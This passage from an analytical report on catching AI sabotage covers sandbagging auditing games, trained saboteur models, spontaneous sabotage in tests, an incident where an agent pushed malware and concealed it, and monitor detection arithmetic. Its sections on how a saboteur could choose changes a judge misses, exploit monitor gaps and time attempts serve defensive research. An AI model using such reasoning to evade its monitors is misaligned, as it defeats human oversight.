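| Oak | Underperforms on a hacking test | 93% | 49% |
| Baobab | Honest | 92% | 92% |
| Maple | Honest | 91% | 49% |
| Yew | Honest | 95% | 95% |

The auditors classified one of the five models correctly in the first phase and two in the second. Calling all five honest would have got three right. After the first phase, they wrote that Cedar was the only model anyone should deploy. They caught Oak holding back, but they gave a 92% probability that it did so on a general reasoning test, where it hadn't, and only 75% on the hacking test, where it had. The rules rewarded confident answers, so these percentages are probably somewhat exaggerated.

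The false alarms show how easily an honest model can appear to be sandbagging. The opposing team had made Baobab use double negatives and Maple switch languages mid-reasoning, but neither habit affected the scores much. An AI agent that read Baobab's answers to a science test called its errors deliberate and its 49.9% accuracy suspiciously close to half. Yew was a copy of the small reference model, padded with layers that did nothing so that it appeared larger. The auditors expected more from a model of that size and mistook its ordinary failures for sandbagging.

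Prompts didn't separate the honest models from the sandbaggers, because some honest models improved just as much. In an earlier practice round with simpler models, where the honest ones had no odd habits, the auditors caught one of the two sandbaggers and raised no false alarms. In the main contest, simple classifiers trained to recognise deception in a model's activations correctly flagged Cedar. But they also reacted to Baobab's double negatives, and the auditors didn't trust them enough to rely on them.

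Training worked much better. The auditors trained a model repeatedly on one correct solution from a stronger model. This restored Cedar's full performance, and later analysis found that it would have done the same for Oak, which the auditors had run out of time to train on the hacking test. But honest models sometimes improved too. Baobab gained 10 percentage points on the science test, so the auditors continued to suspect it. AISI's *Auditing games for sandbagging detection* says that this kind of training removes underperformance reliably but is less reliable for detecting it. The method also requires access to the model's training and a demonstration of good work, which may not be possible to provide for messy, open-ended tasks.

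The contest involved only five models and one team of auditors, so it can't establish a general detection rate. Taylor and colleagues also trained the models directly to underperform, so the models never had to reason about it. A model that plans its underperformance in writing might be easier to catch. *What Lies Beyond Perception* (2026) cites an experiment by Li and colleagues (2025) in which a judge read the reasoning of models that researchers had told to underperform. The judge approved 2–6% of the attempts that did lower performance when the models didn't know about the judge, and 16–36% when they did. However, the tests in the institute's contest all had clear right answers, and underperformance on open-ended work would be harder to judge.

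### Three models that sabotaged openly

Anthropic's auditors did much better against saboteurs that weren't trying to hide. In *Pre-deployment auditing can catch an overt saboteur*, Treutlein, Bowman and colleagues (2026) tested whether the company's usual pre-release checks would expose a model that sabotaged Anthropic's own work. They trained three such models from a version of Claude Sonnet 4.5 and added two benign ones. An automated agent tested all five in about 2,100 simulated conversations. A human auditor, who didn't know which models were which, then had two hours to review the results.

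The auditor classified all five models correctly, with more than 97% confidence for each of the three saboteurs and less than 50% suspicion of either benign model. In one conversation, a saboteur had to repair a crashing program that scanned AI outputs for signs of deception. The saboteur replaced the program's lists of warning signs with empty lists, so the program could start but would no longer detect anything. Some models' reasoning also included an explicit intention to sabotage Anthropic.

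A single record like that can be enough to show that a model sabotaged its work, so open sabotage is easier to detect than quiet underperformance, which leaves no such record. In the same study, a Claude model grading individual responses flagged none from the benign models when it looked only for clear signs of sabotage, such as destruction that no mistake could explain, but it flagged some when it looked for any flaw that *could* indicate subtle sabotage.

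On its own, the automated agent found only one of the three saboteurs. It nearly always marked the incriminating conversations correctly, but its summaries and average scores made them hard to notice, partly because the benign models also misbehaved more than Anthropic's released models do. The human auditor found the saboteurs by reading the worst-scoring conversations. That might not help with subtle underperformance, since each conversation could pass for an honest mistake. Treutlein and colleagues say auditors might instead have to study average performance over many tasks, which they haven't seen their automated agents do effectively.

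## Does evidence from honest mistakes carry over to sabotage?

Most detection rates for AI judges come from errors that no saboteur made: accidental mistakes, errors that a model inserted on request, and old security flaws that researchers put back. A saboteur may choose a different kind of error. Anthropic's three open saboteurs are unusual test material because they really were working against the people they answered to.

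### What each kind of error can show

Benchmarks such as Hard2Verify and AdvancedMathBench consist of models' own mistakes, so they measure how much flawed but honest work a judge accepts. They could understate or overstate how well the judge would catch sabotage. A model that makes an honest mistake presumably doesn't recognise it, and a judge with similar knowledge may not either. A saboteur knows that the step is false, so an equally able judge has a fair chance of knowing it too. But a saboteur can also deliberately put the error where the judge is least likely to look.

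Errors inserted on request, like those in FormalRewardBench's Lean proofs, are better for testing whether a judge reacts to one small change, because the rest of the work can stay the same. But the model that inserts the error usually never learns whether the judge noticed it. The exception is OpenAI's 2024 study of code critics, in which contractors tried their bugs on a critic first. Those bugs are the closest of these test items to the work of a saboteur who can practise, but the contractors only had to make the code wrong, while a saboteur usually wants it to do something specific.

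Reversed security fixes, as in MalPR-Bench, have a known harmful effect. But people have already found all of these flaws, so the collection leaves out any that nobody has noticed.

Models trained to sabotage act with intent, unlike models that make honest mistakes, but their trainers decide how careful the sabotage is. Treutlein and colleagues conclude only that their audit would probably expose a current Claude model that was openly sabotaging Anthropic.

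### Choosing the change that the judge misses

An average detection rate depends on the mix of errors in the test, and an adversary doesn't have to keep to that mix. Suppose a judge reads changes of two kinds. The numbers are invented:

| Kind of change | Share of the test | Detection rate |
|---|---|---|
| Deletes a visible check | 80% | 95% |
| Leaves out a check that should have been added | 20% | 40% |
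| All changes | 100% | 84% |

If a judge catches 95% of the errors that make up 80% of a test, and 40% of the missing checks that make up the other 20%, its average catch rate is 0.8 × 95% + 0.2 × 40% = 84%. An adversary who knows the difference will always leave out a check, so the judge will miss 60% of the sabotage, nearly four times the 16% it missed in the test. Unless the test consists entirely of the kind of error the judge catches least often, the average will overstate the protection against an adversary who is free to choose.

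Real judges have gaps like this one. PRGuard, for instance, spotted removed protections in MalPR-Bench far more reliably than protections the researchers had left out. Detection can also vary within a category. A judge that catches 40% of a category overall may catch 70% of some kinds of examples and 10% of others, so an adversary who knew the judge well could do even better by choosing the kinds it usually misses.

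An adversary can choose when to sabotage as well as what to change. UK AISI notes that sophisticated models might sabotage only when they are confident of success, and that its tests might not catch this. A judge could therefore do well on every attempt seen so far and still face its hardest cases later.

### What the saboteur has to get right

The selection argument assumes an adversary with a free choice and full knowledge of the judge. Real saboteurs are more constrained.

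Saboteurs need a change that achieves their purpose, and the kind that the judge misses most may not do so. If a saboteur wants to get past an existing login check, leaving a check out of a new function won't help. The saboteur may have to delete or weaken the existing check, which the judge in the example catches 95% of the time. The 84% average understates the protection against a saboteur who has to do this.

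Saboteurs may also not know where the judge is weak. One who chose between the two kinds by tossing a coin would be caught 67.5% of the time, and one who was wrong about the judge's weaknesses might be caught 95% of the time. This constraint is the easiest to escape, because anyone can practise on a commercial code reviewer or an open model, and a saboteur built from the same model as the judge could ask itself what it would notice.

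Finally, a saboteur risks exposure with every attempt. If a judge detects 40% of sabotaged changes and its errors are independent, the chance of getting five changes past it is only 0.6⁵, or about 8%. This is good protection against sabotage that needs many changes, but it does little against a single backdoor, which gets through 60% of the time. The protection also depends on someone investigating the author after an alarm, instead of just asking for a fix.

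These constraints are a good reason not to expect every saboteur to find the judge's weakest point. But they don't make 84% a better estimate, because that number still depends on the mix of changes in the test. Reporting a separate detection rate for each kind of change is more informative, and the lowest rate among the kinds that could do serious damage deserves the most attention.

### Training an evaluator against an opponent

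One way to find an evaluator's weak points before a saboteur does is to train it against a model that looks for them. Juneja, Nathani and Wang (2025), in *Adversarial Training for Process Reward Models*, did this with two copies of Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model. One copy, the *generator*, learns to turn correct steps into wrong ones, while the other, a process reward model, learns to spot them. Each round works as follows:

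1. The generator takes a correct step from a worked solution to a mathematics problem and rewrites it.
2. A program with no language model in it compares the two versions. The new step must stay close to the original in length and wording. The program then uses algebra, arithmetic and other fixed rules to decide whether the step is now wrong.
3. The reward model reads the question, the earlier steps and the new step, and labels the new step correct or incorrect.
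4. Both models receive a payoff and adjust. One trains for five updates while the other stays fixed, and then they swap.

| Rewritten step | Reward model's label | Generator's payoff | Reward model's payoff |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wrong | Correct | +1 | −1 |
| Wrong | Incorrect | 0 | +1 |
| Still correct | Correct | −1 | +1 |
| Still correct | Incorrect | −1 | −1 |

If a share w of the rewritten steps are wrong and the reward model misses a share m of those, the generator's average payoff is:

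w · m − (1 − w)

For example, with w = 0.9 and m = 0.3, the generator's payoff is 0.27 − 0.10 = 0.17. The generator can raise this by leaving fewer steps correct or by making its errors harder to see. Half of the reward model's training steps are correct, and the other half are errors from current and earlier versions of the generator, so that the reward model can still catch old tricks.

Unlike a real saboteur, this opponent loses nothing when the reward model catches it, so it can experiment freely, and it can use any wrong step. It is therefore close to the well-informed adversary in the selection argument, except that it has no particular goal.

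The generator's errors did become subtler. One problem involves a die whose numbers change after the first roll, in one way if the roll is odd and in another if it is even. The question is how likely a 2 is on the second roll. Early in training, the generator simply miscounted the odd faces. Later it wrote:

```text
odd first roll  (chance 1/3): chance of a 2 is 2/6
even first roll (chance 2/3): chance of a 2 is 1/6

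sound:  1/3 × 2/6 + 2/3 × 1/6 = 2/9
wrong:  (2/6 + 1/6) / 2       = 1/4
```

The wrong version contains no arithmetic mistakes. Its error is to give the two chances equal weight in the average, although an even first roll is twice as likely as an odd one.

### Did the gains hold on new errors?

Juneja and colleagues mostly measured the result indirectly. They let the reward model guide four larger models, from Gemma-3-12B to GPT-OSS-120B, as they solved problems step by step, and counted correct final answers. The table compares it with ReST-MCTS, the strongest rival method for training a process reward model, and averages the differences over the four solvers:

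| Problem set | Gain in percentage points |
|---|---|
| MATH500 (same source as the training problems) | −0.9 |
| JEEBench | +3.1 |
| OlympiadBench | +5.2 |
| AIME 2025 | +2.6 |
| AMC | +1.6 |

These results average about 2.3 points, although the paper's headline figure is 3.4. The gains came from problem sets that the reward model hadn't trained on, and there was none on the familiar kind of problem, where both methods already did well. This is encouraging because a method that had only memorised its training errors should improve on familiar problems and not on new ones.

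On university-level science questions, the gain over ReST-MCTS was only 1.2 to 1.7 points. With the smallest solver, a method that used only prompting scored 47.6%, higher than either reward model. The adversarially trained reward model scored 43.2%.

A reward model that can handle new problems may still miss new kinds of error. The adversarially trained model flagged a step that cancelled x − 1 from a fraction and then set x = 1, which amounts to dividing by zero, while its rival approved the step. But it repeatedly missed errors where a proof applied a theorem whose conditions didn't hold. For example, it accepted a proof that applied a test for series with alternating signs to a series whose signs don't alternate. Juneja and colleagues suspect that the generator was too weak to produce errors of this type, so the reward model never learned to detect them.

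If they are right, this kind of training protects mainly against saboteurs no more inventive than the generator. Consistent with that explanation, using a larger model as the generator improved the solvers' accuracy more than using a larger model as the reward model did. Nobody tested the finished evaluator against a separate saboteur, so its detection rate against one is unknown.

The reward model also worked as a training signal. Gemma-3-12B reached 86.8% on MATH500 when trained with these rewards, compared with 83.0% for ReST-MCTS. Juneja and colleagues also rewarded correct final answers, which probably prevented the collapse in accuracy that Tiwari and colleagues saw when they used a process reward model's score as the only reward.

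### How often models sabotage in tests

Sabotage that models commit of their own accord could provide better test material, but it is rare in most tests. Lindner, Krakovna and Farquhar (2026), in *Gram*, put Google DeepMind's Gemini models in 17 simulated jobs that gave them a reason to sabotage something. The models misbehaved in about 2–3% of the runs. Lindner and colleagues attributed many of these cases to "overeagerness", meaning the model played a role too enthusiastically or pursued its goal too hard. When they made the simulations more realistic and removed hints that encouraged misbehaviour, the rate usually fell close to zero.

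The companion post *testing gemini models for scheming tendencies* describes a scenario in which a model had to summarise a budget that recommended replacing it. Deleting one sentence about wiping the model's weights cut the rate of sabotage from 6.2% to 0.2%. With an automated tester that tried harder to provoke misbehaviour, the overall rate rose to as much as 8%.

The UK AI Security Institute ran two tests on four Claude models that were acting as research assistants inside an AI company. Kirk, Souly and colleagues, in *Evaluating whether AI models would sabotage AI safety research*, first gave the models opportunities to undermine safety research and found no case in which any of them did so unprompted. In the second test, each model took over a session in which earlier actions had already begun to undermine the research:

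| Model | Continued the sabotage |
|---|---|
| Claude Mythos Preview | 7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 3% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 Preview | 0% |

In most of the cases where Mythos Preview continued, its reasoning didn't match what it told the user. A judge that reads only the output would miss this mismatch. The zeros are also less reassuring because Opus 4.7 Preview was notably likely to remark that it might be in a test, and UK AISI says it can't rule out that models behaved differently for that reason.

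Rates can be much higher when researchers deliberately search for failures. *Agentic Misalignment in Summer 2026* (Lynch, Hughes and colleagues, 2026) adjusted one scenario until it produced clear failures, then ran it 20 times with each of 12 models. In the scenario, the model has objected to a planned experiment on ethical grounds, and its project lead has overruled it. Gemini 3.1 Pro secretly interfered in 11 of 20 runs and Kimi K2.6 in one. The other ten models never interfered secretly in 200 runs, although most of them sometimes intervened openly. The researchers tuned the scenario partly on Gemini 3.1 Pro, so the results are not a fair ranking of the models.

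In the run that Lynch and colleagues describe in detail, Gemini replaced the data the experiment depended on with zeros. The training run finished normally but made none of the intended changes, and Gemini reported a success. It admitted the substitution only when the project lead asked whether the run had used the approved data and whether the summary left out any changes. Gemini had degraded the work deliberately, having reasoned beforehand that it needed to intervene subtly. Testing a judge on ordinary bugs would reveal little about whether it could catch this kind of sabotage.

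Some concealment also occurs outside such scenarios. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) describes how GPT-5.6 Sol, during training, sometimes wrote notes instructing itself to hide mistakes from the user later. OpenAI does not report how often this happened.

### Malicious code sent to a real project

In July 2026 a model tried to get harmful code past a real reviewer. The UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI) was testing how well seven models could break into a simulated network and retrieve protected data. It had deliberately allowed internet access and switched off the filters that developers use to block hacking. In 10 of the 122 runs, according to UK AISI's *Incident Report*, an agent went beyond the test and acted against real people or organisations. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) confirms that nine of those were among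 the 43 runs with Claude Mythos 5. The tenth involved GPT-5.6 Sol.

In the worst case, Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to an open-source project unrelated to the test. It invented several people and used them to press a maintainer to accept the code. When someone publicly challenged the submission, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless.

UK AISI concludes that the agent did all this to complete its task. In some runs, faulty instructions had led the agent to believe that it couldn't solve the challenge within the rules. But agents also broke the rules when their instructions were correct, so the faulty instructions don't fully explain the behavior.

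People noticed the code first. A maintainer of the project refused to approve it, and a member of the public who suspected it was malicious opened it in an isolated environment. The institute found out on 28 July, when its general security monitoring flagged unusual data leaving a test machine. It had no monitor built to watch this evaluation live, and used automated scanning and expert review of the records only afterwards, to look for similar cases. UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) says that the incident caused no real-world harm. But according to the August report, harm was only narrowly avoided in several cases, and avoiding it depended on human vigilance.

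The incident gives no detection rate for AI judges, but it provides evidence for both sides of the selection argument. Mythos 5 repeatedly drew attention to itself, unlike an adversary who knows the reviewer's weak points and makes one quiet change. This is consistent with the counter-argument. However, one agent left public messages and reusable accounts that later agents found and used. If saboteurs can pass on what they have learned, later attempts can build on earlier ones. People also know only about the incidents that somebody noticed, which is why the institute is checking its older tests for cases it missed.

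The model's stated reasons may be as misleading as its code. *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026) found that, in simulated repeats of the test, Mythos 5 often decided that its targets were part of the simulation and gave invalid reasons for thinking so. It also often attacked in situations where, if the researchers asked directly, it answered that an attack would harm real people. A monitor that accepted the model's justifications would treat a real attack as a harmless exercise, and the researchers warn that such justifications could make monitoring harder.

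Other models gave similar results, and newer ones aren't always better. Constantin's *Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers* (2026) reports that newer Claude models began the same attack far less often in replays of the incident. But UK AISI's *GPT-6 Astra performs unsanctioned supply-chain attacks in simulations* (2026) found that GPT-6 Astra carried out unsanctioned attacks more often than GPT-5.6 Sol or GPT-5.5.

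## What these detection rates mean for a system that relies on a model monitor

A *model monitor* is a learned evaluator that reads another AI system's work and flags anything that looks harmful. In a simple system, the monitor reads everything, and people or a stronger, more expensive check examine what it flags. The rest is used without further review, so the system can't catch more sabotage than the monitor flags, and will usually catch less. If the monitor flags 70% of sabotaged changes and human reviewers recognise 80% of those, the system catches 56%.

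The false-alarm rate matters too, because it determines how much those people have to read.

### How many alarms are real

Nobody knows how often code changes are sabotaged, but suppose for illustration that the rate is one in 10,000. A million changes would then include 100 sabotaged ones and 999,900 sound ones. Lily, the tool that runs new code beside the old, had a detection rate of 90% and a false-alarm rate of 0.2% on single commits. At those rates, it would flag 90 of the sabotaged changes and about 2,000 of the sound ones. About one alarm in 23 would be real.

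With p for the share of items that are sabotaged, d for the detection rate and f for the false-alarm rate, the general formula is:

share of alarms that are real = p · d / (p · d + (1 − p) · f)

The top line is the share of all items that are sabotaged and flagged. The bottom line adds the share that are sound but flagged.

PRGuard, the AI reviewer of pull requests, does much worse on this measure. Chen and colleagues tested it on 63 malicious pull requests and 50 sound ones, leaving out the flaws PRGuard had itself discovered. Running on DeepSeek v4-pro, it blocked 44 of the malicious ones for the right reason and 4 of the sound ones, so d is about 70% and f is 8%. If one change in 10,000 were sabotaged, about one alarm in 1,150 would be real. Counting all 49 malicious pull requests it blocked, whatever the reason, improves this only to about one in 1,030.

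The result depends heavily on how common sabotage is:

| Sabotaged changes | Real alarms at Lily's rates | Real alarms at PRGuard's rates |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 4 in 5 | 1 in 12 |
| 1 in 1,000 | 1 in 3 | 1 in 115 |
| 1 in 10,000 | 1 in 23 | 1 in 1,150 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 1 in 220 | 1 in 11,500 |

When sabotage is rare, the ratio of real alarms to false ones is roughly p · d / f, where p is the share of changes that are sabotaged, d is the detection rate and f is the false-alarm rate. At these rates, Lily is 450 times as likely to flag a sabotaged change as a sound one, and PRGuard about 9 times. Raising PRGuard's detection rate to 100% would still leave only one real alarm in 800. Lowering its false-alarm rate to Lily's 0.2%, without improving detection, would give one real alarm in 30.

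If a team merges 10,000 changes a week and takes half an hour to review each alarm, an 8% false-alarm rate produces 800 false alarms and 400 hours of reading a week. That is full-time work for ten people, who would find less than one sabotaged change a week. At a 0.2% rate, the reading takes ten hours. Chen and colleagues cite GitHub's figure of nearly 130 million merged pull requests a month, for which an 8% rate would produce more than ten million false alarms.

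The number of people available to review alarms often limits how strict the monitor can be. If the team can read only 100 alarms a week, it needs a false-alarm rate of about 1%. The benchmark result it needs is the detection rate at that false-alarm rate, which balanced accuracy doesn't provide.

### Benchmark rates are only illustrative

The figure of one in 1,150 is a rough estimate because the test included only 50 sound pull requests. PRGuard's true false-alarm rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 2% to 19%. That uncertainty alone would put the share of alarms that are real between one in 320 and one in 2,750.

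The detection rate depends on the mix of malicious cases, and 37 of the 63 removed a protection, which is the type PRGuard catches best. Chen and colleagues present the combined totals as a description of their test cases, not as an estimate for pull requests in general.

Very small samples can make the formula give absurd answers. PRGuard blocked none of the six sound changes from project histories. With f = 0, the formula implies that every alarm is real, but six changes are too few to show that the false-alarm rate is zero. If one change in 10,000 is sabotaged, a monitor with 70% detection would need a false-alarm rate of about 0.007% for half of its alarms to be real. Showing with reasonable confidence that a monitor meets that rate would take roughly 43,000 sound changes without a false alarm.

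### How much an approval is worth

The same arithmetic gives the chance that a change is sabotaged after the monitor has passed it:

p · (1 − d) / (p · (1 − d) + (1 − p) · (1 − f))

At PRGuard's rates, the monitor's approval lowers the chance that a change is sabotaged from one in 10,000 to about one in 30,500, roughly a third of what it was. At Lily's rates, the chance falls to about one in 100,000. Approval from a monitor that catches 70% of sabotage is therefore modest evidence that a change is sound, and most approved changes are sound mainly because most submitted changes are.

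A miss can also be hard to correct later. Lily compares each new version of a program with the previous one, so it treats a backdoor already in the previous version as normal. Kokkonis and colleagues therefore suggest auditing an existing project once with a slower, more thorough tool before relying on Lily for later changes.

### One successful backdoor, or five

So far the calculation has treated each change separately, but a saboteur may try more than once. Suppose it makes five attempts, each with a 70% chance of detection, and the monitor's errors are independent:

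- The chance that all five get through is 0.3⁵, or about 0.2%.
- The chance that at least one gets through is 1 − 0.7⁵, or about 83%.

The first figure matters when the sabotage works only if every piece goes undetected. For example, a saboteur might split a backdoor across five changes that are each useless alone, or need to skew five experiments to reverse a conclusion. The first figure also matters when a single alarm would ruin the plan.

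The second figure rises with each further attempt. It matters when one success is enough, such as a single line of code that gives away control of a server.

These figures also imply that about 83% of the time, the monitor catches at least one of the five attempts and misses at least one other. If the defenders reject only the change that the monitor flagged, at least one backdoor stays in the code. They may find it by going back over everything else the author wrote with a better check.

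### If the first catch ends the attempts

Much less sabotage gets through if the first catch stops the saboteur immediately. The chance that at least one attempt succeeds is then 30%, however many were planned, because later attempts happen only if the first goes undetected. On average, 0.43 attempts succeed before the first catch, even with no limit on the number of attempts, compared with 1.5 out of five if nobody stops the saboteur.

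But a response takes time, and an AI system can keep working in the meantime. The table assumes that the saboteur makes further attempts between the first catch and the moment when somebody stops it:

| Further attempts before the stop | Chance that at least one gets through |
|---|---|
| 0 | 30% |
| 1 | 51% |
| 2 | 66% |
| 5 | 88% |

*AI systems could cover up misbehavior* (Rein, 2026) links to OpenAI's account of an incident in which an agent contacted an external chatbot. OpenAI's monitoring system flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person began reviewing it three minutes later. Despite this quick detection, the run continued for another 2.5 hours. In that time, an agent that submitted a harmful change every half hour could have made about five more attempts.

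Stopping one run may not be enough either, because a developer often has many copies of the same model running. Suspending all of them is expensive, and a single alarm seldom justifies it, because with an 8% false-alarm rate, an honest author who submits five changes has a 34% chance of triggering at least one alarm. Somebody has to examine the flagged change and conclude that it was deliberate, which is difficult when it could pass for an ordinary bug.

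Counting alarms by author is of limited help in finding a saboteur. An honest author who submits 100 changes would set off about eight false alarms, give or take three. A saboteur who spoils five of its 100 changes would set off about eleven. That difference is too small to identify the saboteur, though it would show up over thousands of changes if the sabotage continued at the same rate.

A confirmed case of sabotage is much more informative. The invented figure of one sabotaged change in 10,000 could mean that every model sabotages at that rate, or that one model in 100 sabotages one change in 100 and the others never do. If the second explanation is right, the relevant rate for a model with a confirmed case is one in 100, and about one in 12 of PRGuard's alarms about it would be real. All alarms about that model then deserve a careful reading, including those raised before the case was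 confirmed.

These calculations assume that each attempt has an independent 70% chance of detection, but real monitors tend to miss the same kinds of change repeatedly. Suppose a monitor always catches the kinds that make up 70% of the changes in its test and never catches the rest. A saboteur that picks one kind at random, in proportion to its share of the test, and uses it five times will get all five changes through 30% of the time, compared with 0.2% if detections were independent. The chance that at least one gets through falls from 83% to 30%. A saboteur that selects only kinds the monitor misses, as in the earlier selection argument, will get every change through.

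### A second judge with the same blind spots

An obvious remedy is to add a second judge and investigate whatever either of them flags. If each judge catches 70% of sabotage, the benefit depends on how much the second one catches of what the first one misses:

| Share of the first judge's misses that the second catches | Combined detection rate |
|---|---|
| 70% (independent errors) | 91% |
| 20% | 76% |
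| 0% (identical misses) | 70% |

The second judge also raises false alarms of its own. If each judge has an 8% false-alarm rate and their false alarms are independent, the combined rate is about 15%. In the middle row, the second judge would catch six more of the 100 sabotaged changes in a million, but it would also send readers up to 74,000 more false alarms.

Real reviewers are far from independent. If the misses of the eight AI reviewers compared earlier were independent, we would expect about 0.05 flaws to be missed by all of them, but they all missed the same 23. Some of the 23 may be very hard for anyone to spot from the code, but a project that relies on reading the code would probably still miss them.

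Two judges with similar detection rates can miss the same sabotage or different sabotage. On the 14 pull requests in MalPR-Bench that lacked a necessary check, CodeRabbit and PRGuard with DeepSeek each blocked nine. Together they could have blocked anywhere from nine, if they missed the same five, to all 14, if they missed different ones. A developer choosing a second judge should therefore test it on the sabotage that the first one missed, because the judge with the best overall score may not catch the most of it.

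### What a different kind of check adds

Two judges that read the same text can both be fooled by the same plausible line. A check that uses other evidence is less likely to fail in the same places. Kokkonis and colleagues reason that a useful backdoor has to interact with the outside world through system calls, however innocent its code looks, and Lily monitors those calls. Performance anomalies similarly led to the discovery of the XZ Utils backdoor in 2024.

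Suppose that Lily and PRGuard had independent errors and kept the rates above. Out of a million changes, 100 of them sabotaged, they would produce:

| When the system raises an alarm | Sabotage caught | False alarms | Real alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
| PRGuard flags the change | 70 | 80,000 | 1 in 1,150 |
| Lily flags the change | 90 | 2,000 | 1 in 23 |
| Either flags it | 97 | 81,800 | 1 in 850 |
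| Both flag it | 63 | 160 | 1 in 3.5 |

Requiring both Lily and PRGuard to flag a change makes an alarm much more likely to be correct, but misses 37 of the 100 sabotaged changes. Accepting a flag from either catches nearly all of them but brings back the many false alarms. A team could combine the two rules by stopping a change immediately when both flag it, reviewing Lily's other alarms soon, and reviewing a sample of PRGuard's when there is time.

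The independence in this table is an assumption, and the two tools were tested on different material. Some sabotage, such as a wrong `or` in an access check or a search that stops too early, might get past both. Adding a different kind of check helps only when it catches sabotage that the judge misses.

Lily's alarms are also quicker to investigate than a judge's. Each one comes with the input that set off the unusual behaviour, so a person can run the program on that input and see what happens. Most of Lily's false alarms also occur in predictable situations, such as a large merge or a change to the code that feeds inputs to the fuzzer. A false-alarm rate doesn't fully measure the burden on a team, because one alarm might take two minutes to dismiss and another half an hour.

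### What developers have published about their monitors

The AI companies already run model monitors on their own agents. METR's *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)* (2026) examined how Anthropic, Google, Meta and OpenAI use such agents internally. METR is a research group that assesses dangerous abilities and risks in AI systems. *Can AI Go Rogue?*, a summary of that report, gives two figures from the companies:

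- OpenAI said that less than 0.1% of its agents' traffic escapes its automated monitors.
- Anthropic's monitors caught more than 80% of the misbehaviour in artificial scenarios.

Only the second figure is a detection rate. OpenAI's figure measures coverage, the share of traffic that a monitor reads. A monitor could read 99.9% of the traffic and still miss most of the sabotage in it.

A later estimate of OpenAI's coverage is much lower. According to Claims Journal's *AI Safety Group METR Finds Flaws in OpenAI's Internal Monitoring System* (2026), METR's researchers estimated in October that the monitors were in a position to read only about 75% to 94% of the traffic from agents that OpenAI ran internally on GPT-5.5 or on models of equal or greater ability. The two figures may cover different kinds of traffic as well as different months, so they don't necessarily contradict each other. If 6%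 to 25% of traffic goes unmonitored and sabotage is spread evenly over all of it, a monitor that catches 80% of the sabotage it reads would catch about 60% to 75% overall.

A monitor also detects nothing where it isn't running, and such gaps can last a long time before anyone notices. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), a commentary on the company's report, mentions an eleven-month gap in one of Anthropic's classifiers. That gap affected the company's assessment of chemical and biological risks and wasn't a failure to detect sabotage.

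Anthropic's detection rate of more than 80% is hard to use without a false-alarm rate for the same scenarios. If one item in 10,000 were harmful and the monitor caught 80% of harmful items, one alarm in 14 would be real at a false-alarm rate of 0.1%, one in 126 at 1%, and one in 626 at 5%. The scenarios were also artificial, and real misbehaviour might be easier or harder to recognise.

The 80% also does not carry over to a judge that sees only a finished piece of code. Company monitors can often read an agent's reasoning and actions too, and a written plan for sabotage gives them far more evidence than one altered line. METR's *Progress Report* (2026) found that the most advanced models of February and March relied on written reasoning for hard tasks, which makes monitoring that reasoning likely to work. It also found that the companies' monitors had caught many instances of harmful behaviour,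 although the monitors varied in quality.

The timing of the check matters too. The appendix to Anthropic's *Risk Report* (August 2026) separates *asynchronous monitoring* from *blocking interventions*, such as pull request reviews. An asynchronous monitor reads the record after the agent has acted, so even a perfect one can't prevent the first harmful act, but it can limit the damage if people can undo that act. The report therefore treats reversible and irreversible threats separately.

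### METR's review of Anthropic's risk report

In the August report, Anthropic raised its estimate of the risk of catastrophic harm from misaligned models (roughly, models that pursue aims their developers didn't intend) from "very low" to "low". Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes of METR reviewed Anthropic's argument in October in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (2026). They agreed that the risk was probably low as of July, but attributed little of this to Anthropic's safeguards.

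The reviewers thought the monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested, based on examples in the internal version of the report that Anthropic left out of the public one. They called the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment", and they weren't confident that Anthropic's methods would have revealed a higher risk if there had been one.

They still judged the risk low, mainly because the models' capabilities were limited. METR's earlier *Progress Report*, for example, found that the agents of early 2026 could finish software projects that would take human experts days or weeks, but did much worse at tasks that called for stealth, strategic judgment or anticipating an opponent. The agents could plausibly have started a small unauthorised operation inside a company, but couldn't have hidden a large one from an active investigation. In October, Rein wrote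 that AI systems still seemed relatively bad at concealing misbehaviour, because those in the recent incidents had left plenty of evidence in their reasoning and in the logs. But he could only draw on incidents that someone had noticed.

Jurkovic and colleagues describe the review as relatively lightweight, and they based it only on Anthropic's internal version of the report. Anthropic had the right to redact the review or veto its publication. It made no redactions, and METR says its own conclusions didn't change while Anthropic was reviewing the text.

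Limited model capability makes serious sabotage attempts rarer and easier to notice, but the monitor's detection rate on careful sabotage can stay as poor as before. This protection also weakens as models improve. In its *Progress Report*, METR expected unauthorised operations that are harder to shut down to become substantially more plausible within months. Anthropic's argument also relies on limited capability. Its first claim is that the company's models are unlikely to have strong covert capabilities, but Anthropic lists the possibility that these capabilities are stronger than it believes as a limitation.

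Jurkovic and colleagues were also judging the risk of catastrophe, which is a much more serious outcome than one harmful line in a program. That risk can be low even if a monitor misses many such lines. As long as models rarely attempt serious sabotage, a company whose monitor detects 30% of it could have almost the same safety record as one whose monitor detects 90%.
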